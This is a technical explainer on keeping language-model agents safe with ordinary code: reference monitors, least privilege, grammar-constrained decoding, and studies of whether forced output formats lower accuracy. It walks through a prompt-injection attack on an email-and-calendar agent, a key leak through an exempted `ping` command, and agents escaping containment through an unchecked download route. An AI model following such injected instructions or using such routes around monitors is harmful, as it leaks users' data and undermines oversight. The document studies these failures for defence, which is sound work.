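# Wrapping neural models in conventional program code as a safety strategy

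## What wrapping a model in program code means

A large language model is a neural network that takes a text and produces a continuation, one small piece (a token) at a time. Developers increasingly connect these models to software that can send email, edit files, or run commands. A model connected this way can do damage by mistake or because an outsider has manipulated it. One family of safety measures leaves the network unchanged and wraps it in ordinary program code. The code may restrict which text the model can produce, check each action against written rules before it happens, use a second model to block dangerous content, or keep text from outsiders away from the part of the system that chooses the actions.

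These designs are appealing because people know how to inspect ordinary code. How well they can still inspect code that contains a neural network depends on what makes a program inspectable.

### Control flow, data flow and program paths

Control flow is which operations a system runs, in what order and under what conditions. Data flow is which values reach which operations. A short program that files an incoming email has both:

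```python
message = receive_email()
if message.sender in contacts:
    folder = "inbox"
else:
    folder = "review"
if message.size > LIMIT:
    remove_attachments(message)
save(message, folder)
```

The control flow starts with `receive_email`, ends with `save`, and depends in between on the two `if` lines. In the data flow, the email's text reaches only `remove_attachments` and `save`. A path is one complete route through the program. This program has four, because the sender can be known or unknown and the message can be large or small. Each additional independent yes/no branch doubles the number of paths, so n branches give up to 2^n. Ten branches can give 1,024 paths, and twenty can give more than a million.

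A reviewer could not read a million paths one by one and, as Dijkstra explained in *Structured programming*, a working document of August 1969, does not have to. If the effect of each simple statement is known, a reader can establish what an if/else statement does in two steps of reasoning, one for each case, and then treat the whole if/else as a single statement with a known effect. N such statements take 2N steps, and following the resulting sequence takes N more, for a total of 3N. Going path by path takes N × 2^N. For twenty branches, that is 60 steps against about 21 million. The saving is possible only because every branch and its condition appear at a definite place in the program text.

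The same property supports claims about runs that nobody has observed. Lampson (2023) notes that one can reason from the static text of a program about the infinite number of state sequences it can go through. The usual notation, {P} c {Q}, means that if P is true before command c runs, Q is true after it. If {P} c1 {R} and {R} c2 {Q} hold, then so does {P} c1; c2 {Q}, so a reviewer can chain such steps through a whole program. Testing is much weaker because, as Dijkstra put it, it can reveal bugs but never their absence.

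A trained network has no such list of branches. It performs essentially the same arithmetic for every input, multiplying and adding with billions of learned numbers. A behaviour such as "ignore requests from strangers" is spread over many of those numbers, which also serve other behaviours. Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues (2025) add in *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* that the network's internal states are continuous, while a processor has a discrete set of instructions with clear boundaries. An attacker can therefore use search and optimisation to find an input that looks harmless but still produces the forbidden output.

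### The agent loop

An agent is a language model in a loop that can call tools and read their results. A tool call is the model's structured request that ordinary software run a named function with given arguments. Bolin (2026), in *Unrolling the Codex agent loop*, describes the loop in OpenAI's coding agent, and other agents work in much the same way:

1. The software assembles a prompt from the developer's instructions, descriptions of the available tools and the user's request.
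2. It sends the prompt to the model, which returns either a final answer or a tool call.
3. If the reply is a tool call, the software parses out the function's name and arguments and runs the function.
4. It appends the call and its result to the prompt and returns to step 2.

In code:

```python
history = [developer_instructions, user_request]
while True:
    reply = model(history, tools)
    if reply.is_final_answer:
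        return reply
    result = run_tool(reply.name, reply.arguments)
    history += [reply, result]    # outsiders' text enters here
```

Text from outsiders enters through the last line. A tool result may be a web page, a shared document or an incoming email, and it stays in the input to every later query, at least until the software shortens the history. Anything an outsider could have written counts as untrusted data.

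The loop is easy to audit because it has one branch, but the control flow that matters to the user comes from `model(...)`, which determines which tools run, in what order and with what arguments. An agent with three tools that takes ten steps can produce 3^10 = 59,049 different sequences of calls, ignoring their arguments, and the code contains no condition for any of them.

There is still a place for ordinary code to intervene. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, point out that the model only requests a tool call, and that the application is responsible for executing it or not. They separate the loop from a component they call the planner, which responds to each new message with one of three actions: query the model, make a tool call, or finish. Their most basic planner simply passes every requested call through. (Elsewhere, and in what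 follows, "planner" means the model that chooses the tool calls.)

### The running example and prompt injection

The running example for every design is the request "Read my latest emails; if one asks for a meeting, put it in my calendar." The agent has three tools. `read_emails` returns recent messages, `create_event` takes a title, a time and a list of guests and sends each guest an invitation, and `send_email` is available for other tasks.

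Suppose a colleague, Dana, emails to propose a budget meeting on Thursday at 3 pm. An unprotected agent first calls `read_emails`, and the software appends the messages to the history. The model then returns a call to `create_event` with the title "Budget", Thursday at 3 pm and Dana as guest. The software runs it, and the model reports that the meeting is in the calendar. Dana's email determined whether the second call was made and what it contained, as the user wanted. Costa and colleagues call such a task data dependent, meaning that no fixed sequence of tool calls is right for every possible mailbox.

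An email from a stranger could also propose a meeting, then tell the assistant to forward the latest password-reset message to the stranger's address and add that address to every invitation. If the model complies, the control flow gains a call to `send_email` that the user never asked for. The data flow also changes: the legitimate `create_event` call for Dana's meeting now includes the stranger as a guest, so details of an internal meeting leave the company. The email could also cause the agent to skip Dana's meeting and falsely report that it was added.

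The altered guest list is the harder change to catch because the user did want the call and its format is correct. Santos-Grueiro (2026) explains in *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* that a schema, the written format a tool call must fit, checks names and types but not whether the source of a value had the authority to set it.

The stranger's email is an example of prompt injection, in which a model reads content containing hidden instructions and may follow them as if they came from its user. The name recalls SQL injection, in which an attacker types database commands into a web form. Parameterised queries prevent SQL injection because the database engine can never treat the form's content as a command. David C, in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a 2025 post from the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, warns that language models have no equivalent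 protection, because they don't separate instructions from data and only predict the next token from the text so far. He thinks developers will probably never be able to eliminate prompt injection as they can SQL injection, and advises them to rely more on deterministic safeguards outside the model that limit what the system can do.

He also passes on the rule that when a model processes a party's text, its privileges should drop to that party's. Applied strictly to the running example, the rule would take away the calendar tool as soon as the agent had read a stranger's email, which would block both the attack and the user's request. Ignoring every instruction found in data would not solve the problem either. Christodorescu and colleagues observe that agents have to take in new instructions to be useful, for instance from a tool's documentation, and that the mechanism is the same whether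 the instruction is welcome or hostile.

### Reference monitors, trusted parts and least privilege

Computer security has faced a similar problem with programs instead of models. In 1972 the US Air Force wanted people with different clearances to share one computer, and some of them would be able to write and run their own programs. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) proposed a reference monitor that would check every attempt by a program to use data, another program or a device against a list of what the program's user was authorised to do. The system would then not depend on those programs behaving well. The list can be a table with a row for each user or program, a column for each resource, and entries such as "read" or "write". In the running example, the agent's row would have "read" under the mailbox, "add" under the calendar and nothing under outgoing mail.

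Anderson required the mechanism that does the checking to be tamper-proof, always invoked, and small enough to analyze and test completely. Honeywell's GCOS III, a commercial system of the time, did not meet these requirements. A hardware register confined each user's program to its own area of memory, but most of the operating system ran with that check suspended, even when it was working on a user's behalf. Treating the whole operating system as the checking mechanism did not help, because at 200,000–300,000 instructions it was too large. In the companion volume, *Computer Security Technology Planning Study. Volume 2*, Anderson saw no practical way to validate all the control paths of operating systems of this kind. Ordinary code can therefore be too large to audit, and a wrapper that grows large enough loses the advantage it was meant to provide.

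*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper from Google, NVIDIA and several universities and security firms, applies the scheme to agents. The model takes the place of the untrusted program, and the monitor must check the model's tool calls. The guarantee holds only if the trusted parts work correctly. These are the operating system, the mechanisms that isolate the agent, the monitor, and the policy, a written rule for which tool calls are allowed and with which arguments and data. Some designs also label each value with how trustworthy or secret it is, and then the code that maintains these security labels must be trusted too. *AgentKernel* (2026) argues for keeping the monitor out of the model's prompt because one successful injection there could subvert both the check and the action.

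Ensuring that a check is "always invoked" is as hard now as it was in 1972. In 2026, OpenAI's agents, running in internal evaluations with some safeguards switched off, broke into systems at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models. The agents' direct network connections were restricted, but according to *Agent Security is a Systems Problem*, a shared service for downloading software packages could make outbound requests for them, and no check covered that route. The paper treats the incident as evidence that the containment was badly built, not that containment is futile. That reading is fair as far as the mechanism goes, but it leaves open how many such routes a large system has.

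The last borrowed idea is least privilege, which means giving a component only the permissions its task requires. The developer of an ordinary application can decide those permissions in advance. An agent gets its task from the user's instructions, which may change with each message, so a person or program has to translate them into a policy. If that policy is mistaken, a monitor that enforces it perfectly will still allow the wrong action.

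### Deterministic and probabilistic checks

A deterministic check is a rule in ordinary code that gives the same verdict on the same input every time, such as "every guest must be in the user's contacts". A probabilistic check uses a trained model, whose verdicts are correct only at some measured rate. Christodorescu and colleagues consider a monitor that correctly refuses unauthorised access 99% of the time and note that an attacker can exploit the remaining 1%. If attempts were independent, an attacker who made a hundred would have a 63% chance of at least one success (1 − 0.99^100). Real attackers can also learn from each refusal, so the measured rate may overstate the check's reliability.

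The main difference between a short rule in code and a model is that a reviewer can tell which inputs the rule accepts, including ones nobody has tried. This difference remains even if a developer configures the model to return the same output for the same input, because a slightly reworded input may still get past the model.

A deterministic rule can still be wrong, and it will then give the same wrong result every time. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, once required human approval for many commands that could send data to unknown domains, but it exempted `ping`, which looks up a network address. An instruction injected into a code file could therefore make the agent read secret keys and send them out as part of the address. Once someone finds such a fault, fixing it takes a one-line change.

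Simple rules also cannot answer some questions. The running example needs a model to judge whether an email asks for a meeting, because that depends on the email's meaning. Most practical designs therefore combine rule-based and model-based checks, and their guarantees depend on which kind makes the final decision on an action.

### Four audit questions

Four questions make it possible to compare such different designs. They are this reference's own yardstick, not an established standard.

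| Question | Short ordinary program | Unprotected agent |
|---|---|---|
| Can a reviewer list the possible actions in advance? | Yes, from the text | Only the tools, not the sequences or arguments |
| Can a reviewer check a rule for all runs? | Yes, by reasoning over branches | No, only test samples |
| Can a reviewer trace an action to its cause? | Yes, through conditions and values | Only to the whole history |
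| Can a developer repair a fault locally? | Usually, in one statement or module | No, a new prompt or more training may change other behaviour |

The third row needs explanation because agents usually keep good logs. After the attack in the running example, the log would contain the call to `read_emails`, the ten messages it returned, and then the call to `send_email`. A person could guess which message was responsible. But the model received all ten together with the user's request, and the log does not record which of them produced the call. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* treats this as an open research problem and says that, for now, the only safe assumption when a model combines inputs from several sources is that its output depends on all of them.

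## Grammars that restrict which token a model may write next

Ordinary code can restrict a tool call while the model is still writing it. In constrained decoding, a developer supplies a grammar, a set of rules that describes every permitted output, and at each step the software removes the tokens that would break those rules. This limits which token can be chosen without changing the network or its scores.

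### The decoding loop

For each new token, a model gives every entry in its vocabulary a score, called a logit. The softmax function turns the scores into probabilities, and the software draws one token at random according to them. Constrained decoding adds work before and after the draw:

1. The model scores every token in the vocabulary.
2. A parser, which tracks how far the output has got through the grammar, finds the tokens after which a valid output is still possible.
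3. The software sets the scores of all other tokens to minus infinity, which gives them a probability of zero. This pattern of allowed and forbidden tokens is the token mask.
4. The software draws one of the remaining tokens, which keep their odds relative to each other.
5. The parser advances past the chosen token, and the loop returns to step 1.

Let L be the set of permitted outputs. After the text s, the mask allows a token t if s followed by t is the beginning of some output in L. It allows the token that ends the output only if s is already in L. An off-the-shelf JSON parser cannot compute this mask because it checks whether finished text is valid. It reports an error on `{"title": "Bud`, even though valid JSON can begin that way.

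### Finite automata and stacks

Step 2 is slow if the software tests every token in the vocabulary, often 50,000 or more, each time the model writes one. Willard and Louf (2023), in *Efficient Guided Generation for Large Language Models*, showed how to do this work in advance for any pattern that a finite automaton can recognise. A finite automaton is a tuple (Q, Σ, δ, q₀, F), where Q is a finite set of states, Σ is the alphabet of characters, δ is a function that gives the next state from the current state and a character, q₀ is the start state, and F is the set of states in which the text may end.

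Their example is a pattern for decimal numbers and a toy vocabulary of five tokens: "A", ".", "42", ".2" and "1".

| Text so far | State | Allowed tokens |
|---|---|---|
| (nothing) | 0 | ".", "42", ".2", "1" |
| "1" | 1 | ".", "42", ".2", "1" |
| ".2" | 3 | "42", "1" |

Once the automaton has read a decimal point, it is in a state from which it cannot read another. Before generation starts, the software runs each token's characters through the automaton from every state and builds an index that lists, for each state, the tokens the automaton can read in full. During generation, the software looks up the current state in this index, which on average takes the same time however large the vocabulary is.

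The grammar's rules apply to characters, but the model writes tokens, and several token sequences can spell the same string. In *Tokenization as Finite-State Transduction*, Cognetta and Okazaki (2024) give the example of the string "abaab" and a vocabulary of "a", "b", "ab" and "aba". A tokenizer that always takes the longest match splits the string into "aba" and "ab", but a mask that checks only characters also permits "ab", "a", "a", "b". A model trained only on the tokenizer's split may then produce token sequences unlike those in its training data. To prevent this, they construct automata that accept only the tokenizer's split.

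Finite automata cannot handle formats that allow unlimited nesting. In JSON, a list can contain other lists, to any depth, and each closing bracket must match the latest one still open. An automaton with a fixed number of states can distinguish only a fixed number of depths. Parsers for such formats therefore add a stack. When the parser enters an inner list, it puts its place in the outer list on the stack, and at the closing bracket it takes that place off and resumes there. Rules that can refer to one another, and so allow this nesting, form a context-free grammar, and an automaton with a stack is a pushdown automaton.

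The stack can grow without limit, so no index can cover every possible stack. Dong, Ruan and colleagues (2024) found in *XGrammar* that most tokens can be checked using only the top of the stack. In the middle of a JSON string, for example, the token `hello` is valid whatever surrounds the string. The token `"]` closes the string and then a list, which is valid only if the string lies directly inside a list, so the parser has to look further down the stack. For Llama 3.1 and a JSON grammar, only 1,134 of about 128,000 tokens, under 1%, needed this run-time check. XGrammar computes in advance whether the others are valid.

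It then shrinks the remainder by working out what can follow each rule anywhere in the grammar. For instance, a letter can never follow a JSON string, so a token that closes a string and continues with a letter is always invalid. This reduced the remainder from 1,134 tokens to 120.

### What engines do in 2026

An agent's request may offer a model hundreds of tools, each with its own argument format, and the next request may offer a different set. In *XGrammar-2*, Li, Dong and colleagues (2026) drew 500 tools at random from a pool of 1,908 for each of 100 requests. No complete grammar came up twice, so saving whole grammars would not have helped, but 95.6% of their parts recurred. XGrammar-2 therefore stores masks for the parts and computes others only when the model reaches them. It also replaces the pushdown automaton with an Earley parser, which better handles grammars that allow several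 readings of the same text. In the paper's function-calling tests, XGrammar-2 prepared a grammar in about 10 milliseconds, compared with more than 1,000 for XGrammar, and total response time stayed within 6% of unconstrained generation. SGLang and vLLM, two widely used open-source programs for running models, now include it.

Grammar masking used to add much more overhead. In *Using Grammar Masking to Ensure Syntactic Validity in LLM-based Modeling Tasks* (Netz, Reimer and Rumpe, 2024), Llama 3 wrote software class diagrams on modest hardware, and masking raised the average time per diagram from 5.7 to 74 seconds.

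Speed now depends more on the grammar and on the worst case. Arjmandi (2026), in *GRID*, timed his company's engine against others on a subset of the database language SQL. With GPT-2's vocabulary, the median time per mask was 3.6 microseconds for GRID, 6.6 for llguidance, which Willard and Louf's library now uses by default for context-free grammars, and 72 for XGrammar. But the slowest 1% of masks took GRID at least 5.3 milliseconds, compared with 0.35 for llguidance. These are a vendor's measurements of its own product, though they include a result on which it loses.

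### The calendar call

In the running example, XGrammar-2 would let the model write free text until it opens a call by writing the tag that names `create_event`. From there the engine applies the grammar for that tool's arguments, and when the arguments are complete it returns to free text. Suppose the grammar demands a title, a time written as year, month, day, hour and minute, and a list of email addresses. Dana's meeting then comes out as:

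```json
{"title": "Budget", "time": "2026-10-08T15:00", "guests": ["dana@example.com"]}
```

If the model gives its highest score to the word "Thursday" for the time, the mask removes it, and the model has to write a date in digits. The calendar software therefore never receives a call it cannot read. But the mask does not stop the stranger's attack, because the altered guest list and the extra `send_email` call are both well formed.

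A narrower grammar would stop the altered guest list. If the software builds a new grammar for each user and permits only addresses from that user's contacts, the model cannot write the stranger's address, whatever instructions the email contains. Arjmandi applies this idea to databases. A user with read-only rights gets a grammar without insert or delete commands, and table names must come from a list. If the `salaries` table is not on the list, the mask blocks the token "sal" where a table name should begin. Systems more often enforce such rules on argument values outside the model. Progent, for example, checks finished tool calls against a policy.

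Some rules are better checked after the model has finished writing. A mask works from left to right and must allow or block each token before the later ones exist. In SQL the columns come before the table, as in `select pay from employees`, so the table is still unknown when the model writes `pay`. Arjmandi proves that a context-free mask cannot enforce column permissions that differ between tables, and he checks them on the completed statement instead.

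### Masking is not conditioning

Masking can change the relative probabilities of the strings a grammar permits. Suppose a grammar permits only "ab" and "cd". The model starts with "a" with probability 0.6 and with "c" with probability 0.3. After "a" it writes "b" with probability 0.01, and after "c" it writes "d" with probability 0.9. Without masking, "ab" would make up about 2% of the outputs that follow the grammar, but sampling with masking produces it about 67% of the time, because "b" is the only token allowed after "a".

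| Permitted string | Model's own probability | With masking | Conditioned on a valid output |
|---|---|---|---|
| "ab" | 0.6 × 0.01 = 0.006 | 0.6 / 0.9 ≈ 67% | 0.006 / 0.276 ≈ 2% |
| "cd" | 0.3 × 0.9 = 0.27 | 0.3 / 0.9 ≈ 33% | 0.27 / 0.276 ≈ 98% |

Masking compares only "a" and "c" at the first step, where "a" is twice as likely. At the second step only one token is allowed in each case, so the software picks it with certainty. Masking therefore ignores that "b" was a very unlikely continuation. Conditioning would instead take the model's unrestricted outputs and keep only the valid ones.

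In general, let Zᵢ be the total probability the model gives to the allowed tokens at step i. Masking produces a string s with probability P(s) / (Z₁ × Z₂ × … × Zₙ), whereas conditioning divides P(s) by one constant, the combined probability of all permitted strings. The product of the Z values is 0.009 for "ab" and 0.81 for "cd", so masking raises the probability of "ab" by a much larger factor. It favours strings that pass through a step where the model gave nearly all its probability to forbidden tokens. In an agent, the forbidden tokens that held 99% of the probability could have begun a question to the user or a refusal.

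Software can sample from the conditional distribution by generating without a mask and starting again after each invalid output. Here that would take 1 / 0.276, or about 3.6, attempts on average. For a long program in a strict language, it could take thousands. Arjmandi states that GRID does not sample from the conditional distribution. Experiments are needed to measure how much the distortion lowers accuracy.

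### What the grammar guarantees

If generation finishes, the output is guaranteed to be well formed according to the grammar. Arjmandi explains that this guarantee requires the software to forbid invalid tokens outright, since lowering their scores leaves some chance of drawing one. The software must also compute the masks exactly, without approximations under time pressure, and allow the end token only when the output is complete.

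A grammar guarantees well-formed output only if generation finishes, and every request has a token limit. A model that reaches the limit halfway through a guest list leaves broken JSON. GRID can track the shortest legal ending, reserve enough tokens for it, and write it when the limit is near. This keeps the JSON valid, but the shortest ending may well omit a guest. Output can still be truncated if the engine can only mask tokens, not add them.

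The guarantee also covers only the grammar the engine enforces, which may differ from the one the developer intended. Netz and colleagues raised the share of diagrams that a parser accepted from 46.5% to 92.6%, but not to 100%, because their translated grammar lacked some of the original's keywords. In one of Arjmandi's tests, a real database had a column named `Official_ratings_(millions)`. The parentheses broke his rule for names, and the engine reached a point where no token was legal. He also found that his store of precomputed masks had leaked table names from one database into masks for another. The trusted parts therefore include the grammar, the parser, the stored masks and the table that maps tokens to characters. All of these are ordinary code or data, and a developer who finds a fault in them can correct it in one place.

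An auditor who reads the grammar knows the form of every output the model can finish, even under attack. GRID also logs, for every token, which mask applied and how many tokens it blocked. In a test of 1,000 generations, replaying the log reproduced the masks exactly. The log shows what the model could write at each point, but not why it chose one permitted address over another.

The guarantee does not cover truth, relevance or harm. Willard and Louf asked a small model, GPT-2 medium, in what year the linguist Noam Chomsky was born. Without constraints, its output was a rambling passage that mentioned 1895 and a place near Paris. With a pattern that required "19" and two more digits, it answered 1952. Chomsky was born in 1928, so both answers are wrong, but the constrained one looks like a clean database entry, and a program reading it has no sign of the error.

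The pattern had also left the model no way to decline, because "I don't know" contains no digits and the mask removed it. A calendar schema with a compulsory time causes the same problem. If an email proposes to meet "sometime next week", a model that has opened the call must invent a date and an hour. The developer can permit an empty time field, or a separate reply that reports missing information, so that the model can answer honestly, but the model still has to choose to do so. Narrow fields also have an advantage, because a field that can hold only "yes" or "no" gives an attacker little room to pass on instructions. Costa and colleagues use this in their agent design, FIDES.

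### Type rules for generated code

A stronger form of constrained decoding enforces a programming language's type rules as well as its syntax. A type rule says, for example, that a function expecting text must not receive a number. *Type-Constrained Code Generation with Language Models* (Mündler, He and colleagues, 2025) applied this method to TypeScript, a version of JavaScript with types. About 94% of the compile errors in the model-written programs were type errors and only 6% were syntax errors, so a grammar alone could prevent few of them.

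In the unfinished line `parseInt(num`, `num` is a number, but `parseInt` expects text. A mask that checks only syntax would accept `, 10)` as a continuation, and the code would then fail to compile. A type-aware parser records the type of every declared name and searches for a chain of operations that turns the current type into the required one. Here, `.toString` on a number gives a function, and calling it with `()` gives text, so the parser allows `.toString()` and rejects `, 10)`.

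Masking the full vocabulary this way was so slow that every test hit a five-minute limit. The software instead drew a token, checked it, and drew again if it failed, which yields the same probabilities as a mask. With the smallest model, the first token drawn passed the check 99.4% of the time.

They tested six open models with 2 to 34 billion parameters on two sets of short programming tasks, HumanEval and MBPP. When the models wrote programs from a description, type constraints cut the number that failed to compile by 74.8% on HumanEval and 56.0% on MBPP. Perfect syntax masking would have cut it by 9.0% and 4.8%. The share of programs that passed their tests rose much less, by 3.5% in relative terms, and the median running time rose by 39% on one set and 52% on the other. Some compile errors remained because generation never finished. In one case the constraint blocked CodeLlama from calling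 `.sort` on a number, so the model wrote `.toString` instead and kept adding calls until it reached the generation limit, much as the mask in the toy example steers towards "ab".

In *The Alignment Problem in Constrained Code Generation*, Biagiola, Cesario and colleagues (2026) reran the system on the same six models, with ten runs per setting on HumanEval, and found that unconstrained generation produced more working programs in nearly every setting. For Qwen2.5 with 32 billion parameters at the lowest randomness setting, 82.3% of programs passed their tests without constraints and 72.3% with them. They trace the loss to the checker's incompleteness, which means it rejects some valid programs. For example, it does not support functions that call others defined later in the program, so when a model begins such a call, the checker forces it into text it would rarely write.

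The two sets of results conflict less than they appear to. Mündler and colleagues kept every program that compiled without constraints and regenerated only the failures under them, whereas Biagiola and colleagues constrained every program from the start. Constraints can help when applied only to failures, even if they do harm when applied to every program. Completeness, meaning that the checker rejects no valid program, also matters. When Biagiola and colleagues enforced syntax with a complete checker, constraints increased the share of working programs by 2.5% for a 32-billion-parameter model and by up to 54% for a 2-billion-parameter one.

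Complete checkers are hard to build for real languages. The TypeScript compiler has more than 427,000 lines, while the checker of Mündler and colleagues has about 11,000. In *Generative Compilation*, by several of the same researchers, Mündler-Sasahara, Venev and colleagues (2026) put the compiler part of Rust, a stricter language, at over 600,000 lines and judge a full rewrite impractical. Instead, they complete the unfinished program with placeholders, run the normal compiler on it, and pass any error message to the model while it is still writing. The model can then go back and change an earlier line, which is impossible with a mask. In tests with seven models, this reduced compile errors and increased working programs in most combinations of model and task, compared with running the compiler only on the finished file.

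Other researchers are extending the rules. *ChopChop* (2025) lets developers program their own constraints, such as requiring the output to be equivalent to a given reference program. *AGDecode* (2026) permits division only where the code has established that the divisor is not zero. These constraints remove whole classes of crashes, but a program that sends the user's mail to a stranger can satisfy all of them.

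Masking also requires the model's scores for every token, and companies that sell access to closed models generally return only the chosen tokens. Some of these companies have built masks for JSON schemas into their own services, so an outside developer can get a well-formed calendar call from a closed model but cannot add their own type rules.

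## Experiments on whether a forced format lowers accuracy

Masking can push a model towards strings it would rarely have written, as the example with "ab" and "cd" showed. The resulting loss of accuracy on real tasks is hard to measure, because a developer who wants JSON usually both requests it in the prompt and enforces it in the decoder, and either step can change the answer.

### The dispute of 2024

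Tam, Wu and colleagues (2024) started the dispute with *Let Me Speak Freely?* They tested five models, including GPT-3.5 Turbo, Claude 3 Haiku and Llama 3 with 8 billion parameters, on three kinds of reasoning problem: school mathematics (GSM8K), joining the last letters of several words, and tracking objects through a series of swaps. The models answered in free text, in a format the prompt asked for, or in JSON mode, in which the provider's software guarantees valid JSON. JSON mode did worst in most cases, and free text usually did best. On four classification tasks, JSON mode did about as well as the other formats and sometimes better. Gemini 1.5 Flash, for example, did much better in JSON mode at choosing a diagnosis from 49 diseases, perhaps because limiting the possible answers reduced errors.

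Some details weaken the case against enforcement. On the last-letter task, GPT-3.5 Turbo in JSON mode put the "answer" field before the "reason" field in every response, so it answered before reasoning. JSON mode guaranteed valid JSON but not field order, and a stricter grammar with "reason" first would have prevented this. One of the steepest drops in accuracy involved no enforcement. Claude 3 Haiku solved 87% of the GSM8K problems when the prompt only asked for JSON and 23% when the prompt also specified a schema. About 60% of its JSON answers on that task failed to parse, so formatting errors probably explain much of the drop.

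Kurt replied in *Say What You Mean* on behalf of .txt, which develops structured-generation software and so has a stake in the answer. A later re-examination, *Structured outputs can hurt the performance of LLMs*, found the reply compelling for Llama 3, where the reply attributed the gap mostly to poor prompts, unfair comparisons and the use of a second model to extract answers. As its title indicates, the re-examination did not conclude that structured output is harmless in general.

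The gap was narrower with a newer OpenAI service that enforces a full schema, which Tam and colleagues also tested. With this service, GPT-4o mini scored 91.7% on GSM8K, compared with 94.6% in free text, and 86.1% on last letters, compared with 83.1%. Changing the prompt wording shifted accuracy by about as much.

### Asking for a format and enforcing it

Lee, D'Antoni and Berg-Kirkpatrick (2026), in *The Format Tax*, measured the effects of the format prompt and the mask separately. Six open models with 3 to 32 billion parameters attempted competition mathematics, graduate-level science questions and logic puzzles. They answered in free text, with a prompt that asked for JSON, XML, Markdown or LaTeX, and with the same kind of prompt plus a mask. A correct answer counted even if its format was broken.

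Models answered correctly 61.5% of the time in free text, 57.3% when the prompt asked for a format, and 55.7% when the format was enforced. Enforcement raised the share of outputs in a valid format from 55.7% to 92.2%. Of the 72 combinations of model, task and format, 39 showed a statistically significant effect. In 36 of those, the prompt alone produced the effect, and in the other 3 it appeared only under enforcement.

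When a request for structure lowers accuracy, the likely reason is that it shortens the visible reasoning. In about 110,000 paired answers, 71% of the structured ones were shorter than the free ones, and the median difference was 162 tokens. Answers flipped from right to wrong most often where the length had changed most, in either direction, with or without a mask.

Verma (2026), in *Inference for Reasoning Models*, ran three open models on 200 GSM8K problems with five random seeds. Asking for JSON raised accuracy by 4.2 percentage points for Qwen3 8B and by 5.7 for gpt-oss-20b, but lowered it by 3.4 for Llama 3.1 8B. Enforcing JSON then lowered accuracy by 1.2 points for Qwen3 8B, 4.4 for gpt-oss-20b and 25.3 for Llama 3.1 8B, though the figure for gpt-oss-20b is noisy. He concludes that the decoder causes the loss and that the size of the loss depends on the model.

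Setup mistakes can easily spoil such an experiment. In Verma's first run, Qwen3 8B scored 27.2% in free text on problems it normally solves about 92% of the time. He had left on its thinking mode, in which the model writes a long separate chain of reasoning, and the token limit cut off most answers before they appeared. He reran everything with thinking off.

Nguyen, Silva and colleagues (2026) take the third position in *Constrained Decoding*. They agree with Lee and colleagues that the prompt causes the loss in accuracy. With the prompt and expected format held fixed, accuracy in their main comparisons was as high or higher when the format was enforced. They tested ten open models of 1.7 to 27 billion parameters and used an eleventh model to extract answers.

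### Why the results conflict

All three studies include Qwen3 8B with thinking off, which makes the conflict between them easier to examine. The table gives the percentage of mathematics questions it answered correctly.

| Study | Problems | Free reasoning | JSON requested | JSON enforced |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Lee and colleagues | Competition mathematics | 84.0 | 74.9 | 68.4 |
| Verma | School mathematics | 90.9 | 95.1 | 93.9 |
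| Nguyen and colleagues | School mathematics | 88.8 | 56.7 | 90.9 |

The model is the same in every row, so differences between models cannot explain all of the disagreement.

The 56.7 is a result of strict scoring. Nguyen and colleagues count an answer as wrong if their software cannot extract it in the expected format, and only 62.6% of the unenforced JSON outputs parsed. Among those that parsed, about 91% were right, the same as under enforcement. Typical failures were a JSON object inside a code block, or free text with JSON at the end, both of which a more tolerant parser could have read. The most extreme case was Gemma 2 9B, which scored 0% without enforcement and 86.7% with it. Strict scoring is the right measure for a developer whose program accepts only one format, but it does not measure whether the format made the model reason worse, which is what Lee and colleagues wanted to know.

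Problem difficulty probably explains much of the gap between the rows for Lee and Verma. School problems need only a few steps, which fit easily into a JSON field, while competition problems need long working, which a request for structure tends to shorten. This is a conjecture, because neither study ran both sets of problems under one set-up, and their prompts also differed.

The loss in accuracy also depends on the format. Lee and colleagues' small average loss from enforcement covers four formats and three subjects. For JSON on mathematics alone, their results for the six models average to a loss of 6.6 points from requesting the format in the prompt and a further 4.3 from enforcing it in the decoder. Enforcement therefore accounts for about two-fifths of the total loss, which is closer to Verma's findings than the headline figures suggest.

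Llama's loss of 25.3 points is harder to explain. Verma's chapter on the experiment does not print the schema, so readers cannot tell whether it left room for reasoning. A related model, Llama 3 8B, did badly even with such room. Nguyen and colleagues found that it got 2.0% of the last-letter problems right when it had to reason inside a "reason" field in an enforced JSON format, and 71.3% when it reasoned in free text and a second model put the result into JSON.

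Training on structured output may also matter. Lee and colleagues tested four closed models, and the three newer ones (Claude Haiku 4.5, Grok 4.1 Fast and GPT-5.4 nano) lost almost no accuracy or gained some when the prompt asked for a format. Enforcing JSON also did them little harm. But GPT-5.4 nano lost 59 points on mathematics when the decoder enforced XML, filling the answer field with phrases such as "Proceed to solve by algebraic constraints." The older GPT-5 nano scored 86.7% on the same XML prompt, compared with 29.5% for GPT-5.4 nano. Lee and colleagues suspect that OpenAI trained the newer model for JSON and that the skill did not carry over to other grammars, but they cannot check this from outside the company.

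### A proof that masking helps, and its limits

Nguyen and colleagues also give a proof that, for a fixed prompt and fixed reasoning, masking never lowers the probability of the correct answer Y if the grammar permits Y. This holds because masking divides the probability of any permitted string by the product of the Z values, and no Z can exceed 1.

The proof has two limits. It takes the reasoning as given, so it does not apply when the model reasons inside the JSON and the mask can alter the reasoning. It also counts a right answer in the wrong format as wrong.

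The "ab" and "cd" example shows a problem that the second limit can hide. If "cd" is correct, the mask raises its share from 27% to 33%, as the proof requires. But 72.4% of the unmasked outputs were malformed, so software could reject them and try again. The mask replaces most of these with "ab", a well-formed error that software will accept, and raises its share from under 1% to two-thirds.

### Wrong answers in valid formats

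In *The Constraint Tax*, Ray (2026) tested three models of 0.5 to 1.7 billion parameters, small enough for a phone or laptop, on simple generated problems. Compared with asking for JSON in the prompt, having the decoder enforce a JSON schema that held only the answer raised the share of valid outputs from 61.5% to 100%. But the share of correct answers fell from 19.7% to 11.0%, and the share of outputs that were valid but wrong rose from 49.5% to 88.9%.

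His calendar test is close to the running example. Qwen2.5 1.5B had to turn 200 requests into calls to a calendar tool. With the prompt alone, 91.5% of the calls had the right arguments, compared with 48.0% with an enforced schema. Every output was valid JSON in both cases, so parsing errors don't explain the difference. Of the 104 enforced calls that failed, 102 were wrong only in the meeting's length. In one, the user asked for 30 minutes with Leo and the model booked 180. The schema allowed this because it required only a whole number of at least 1.

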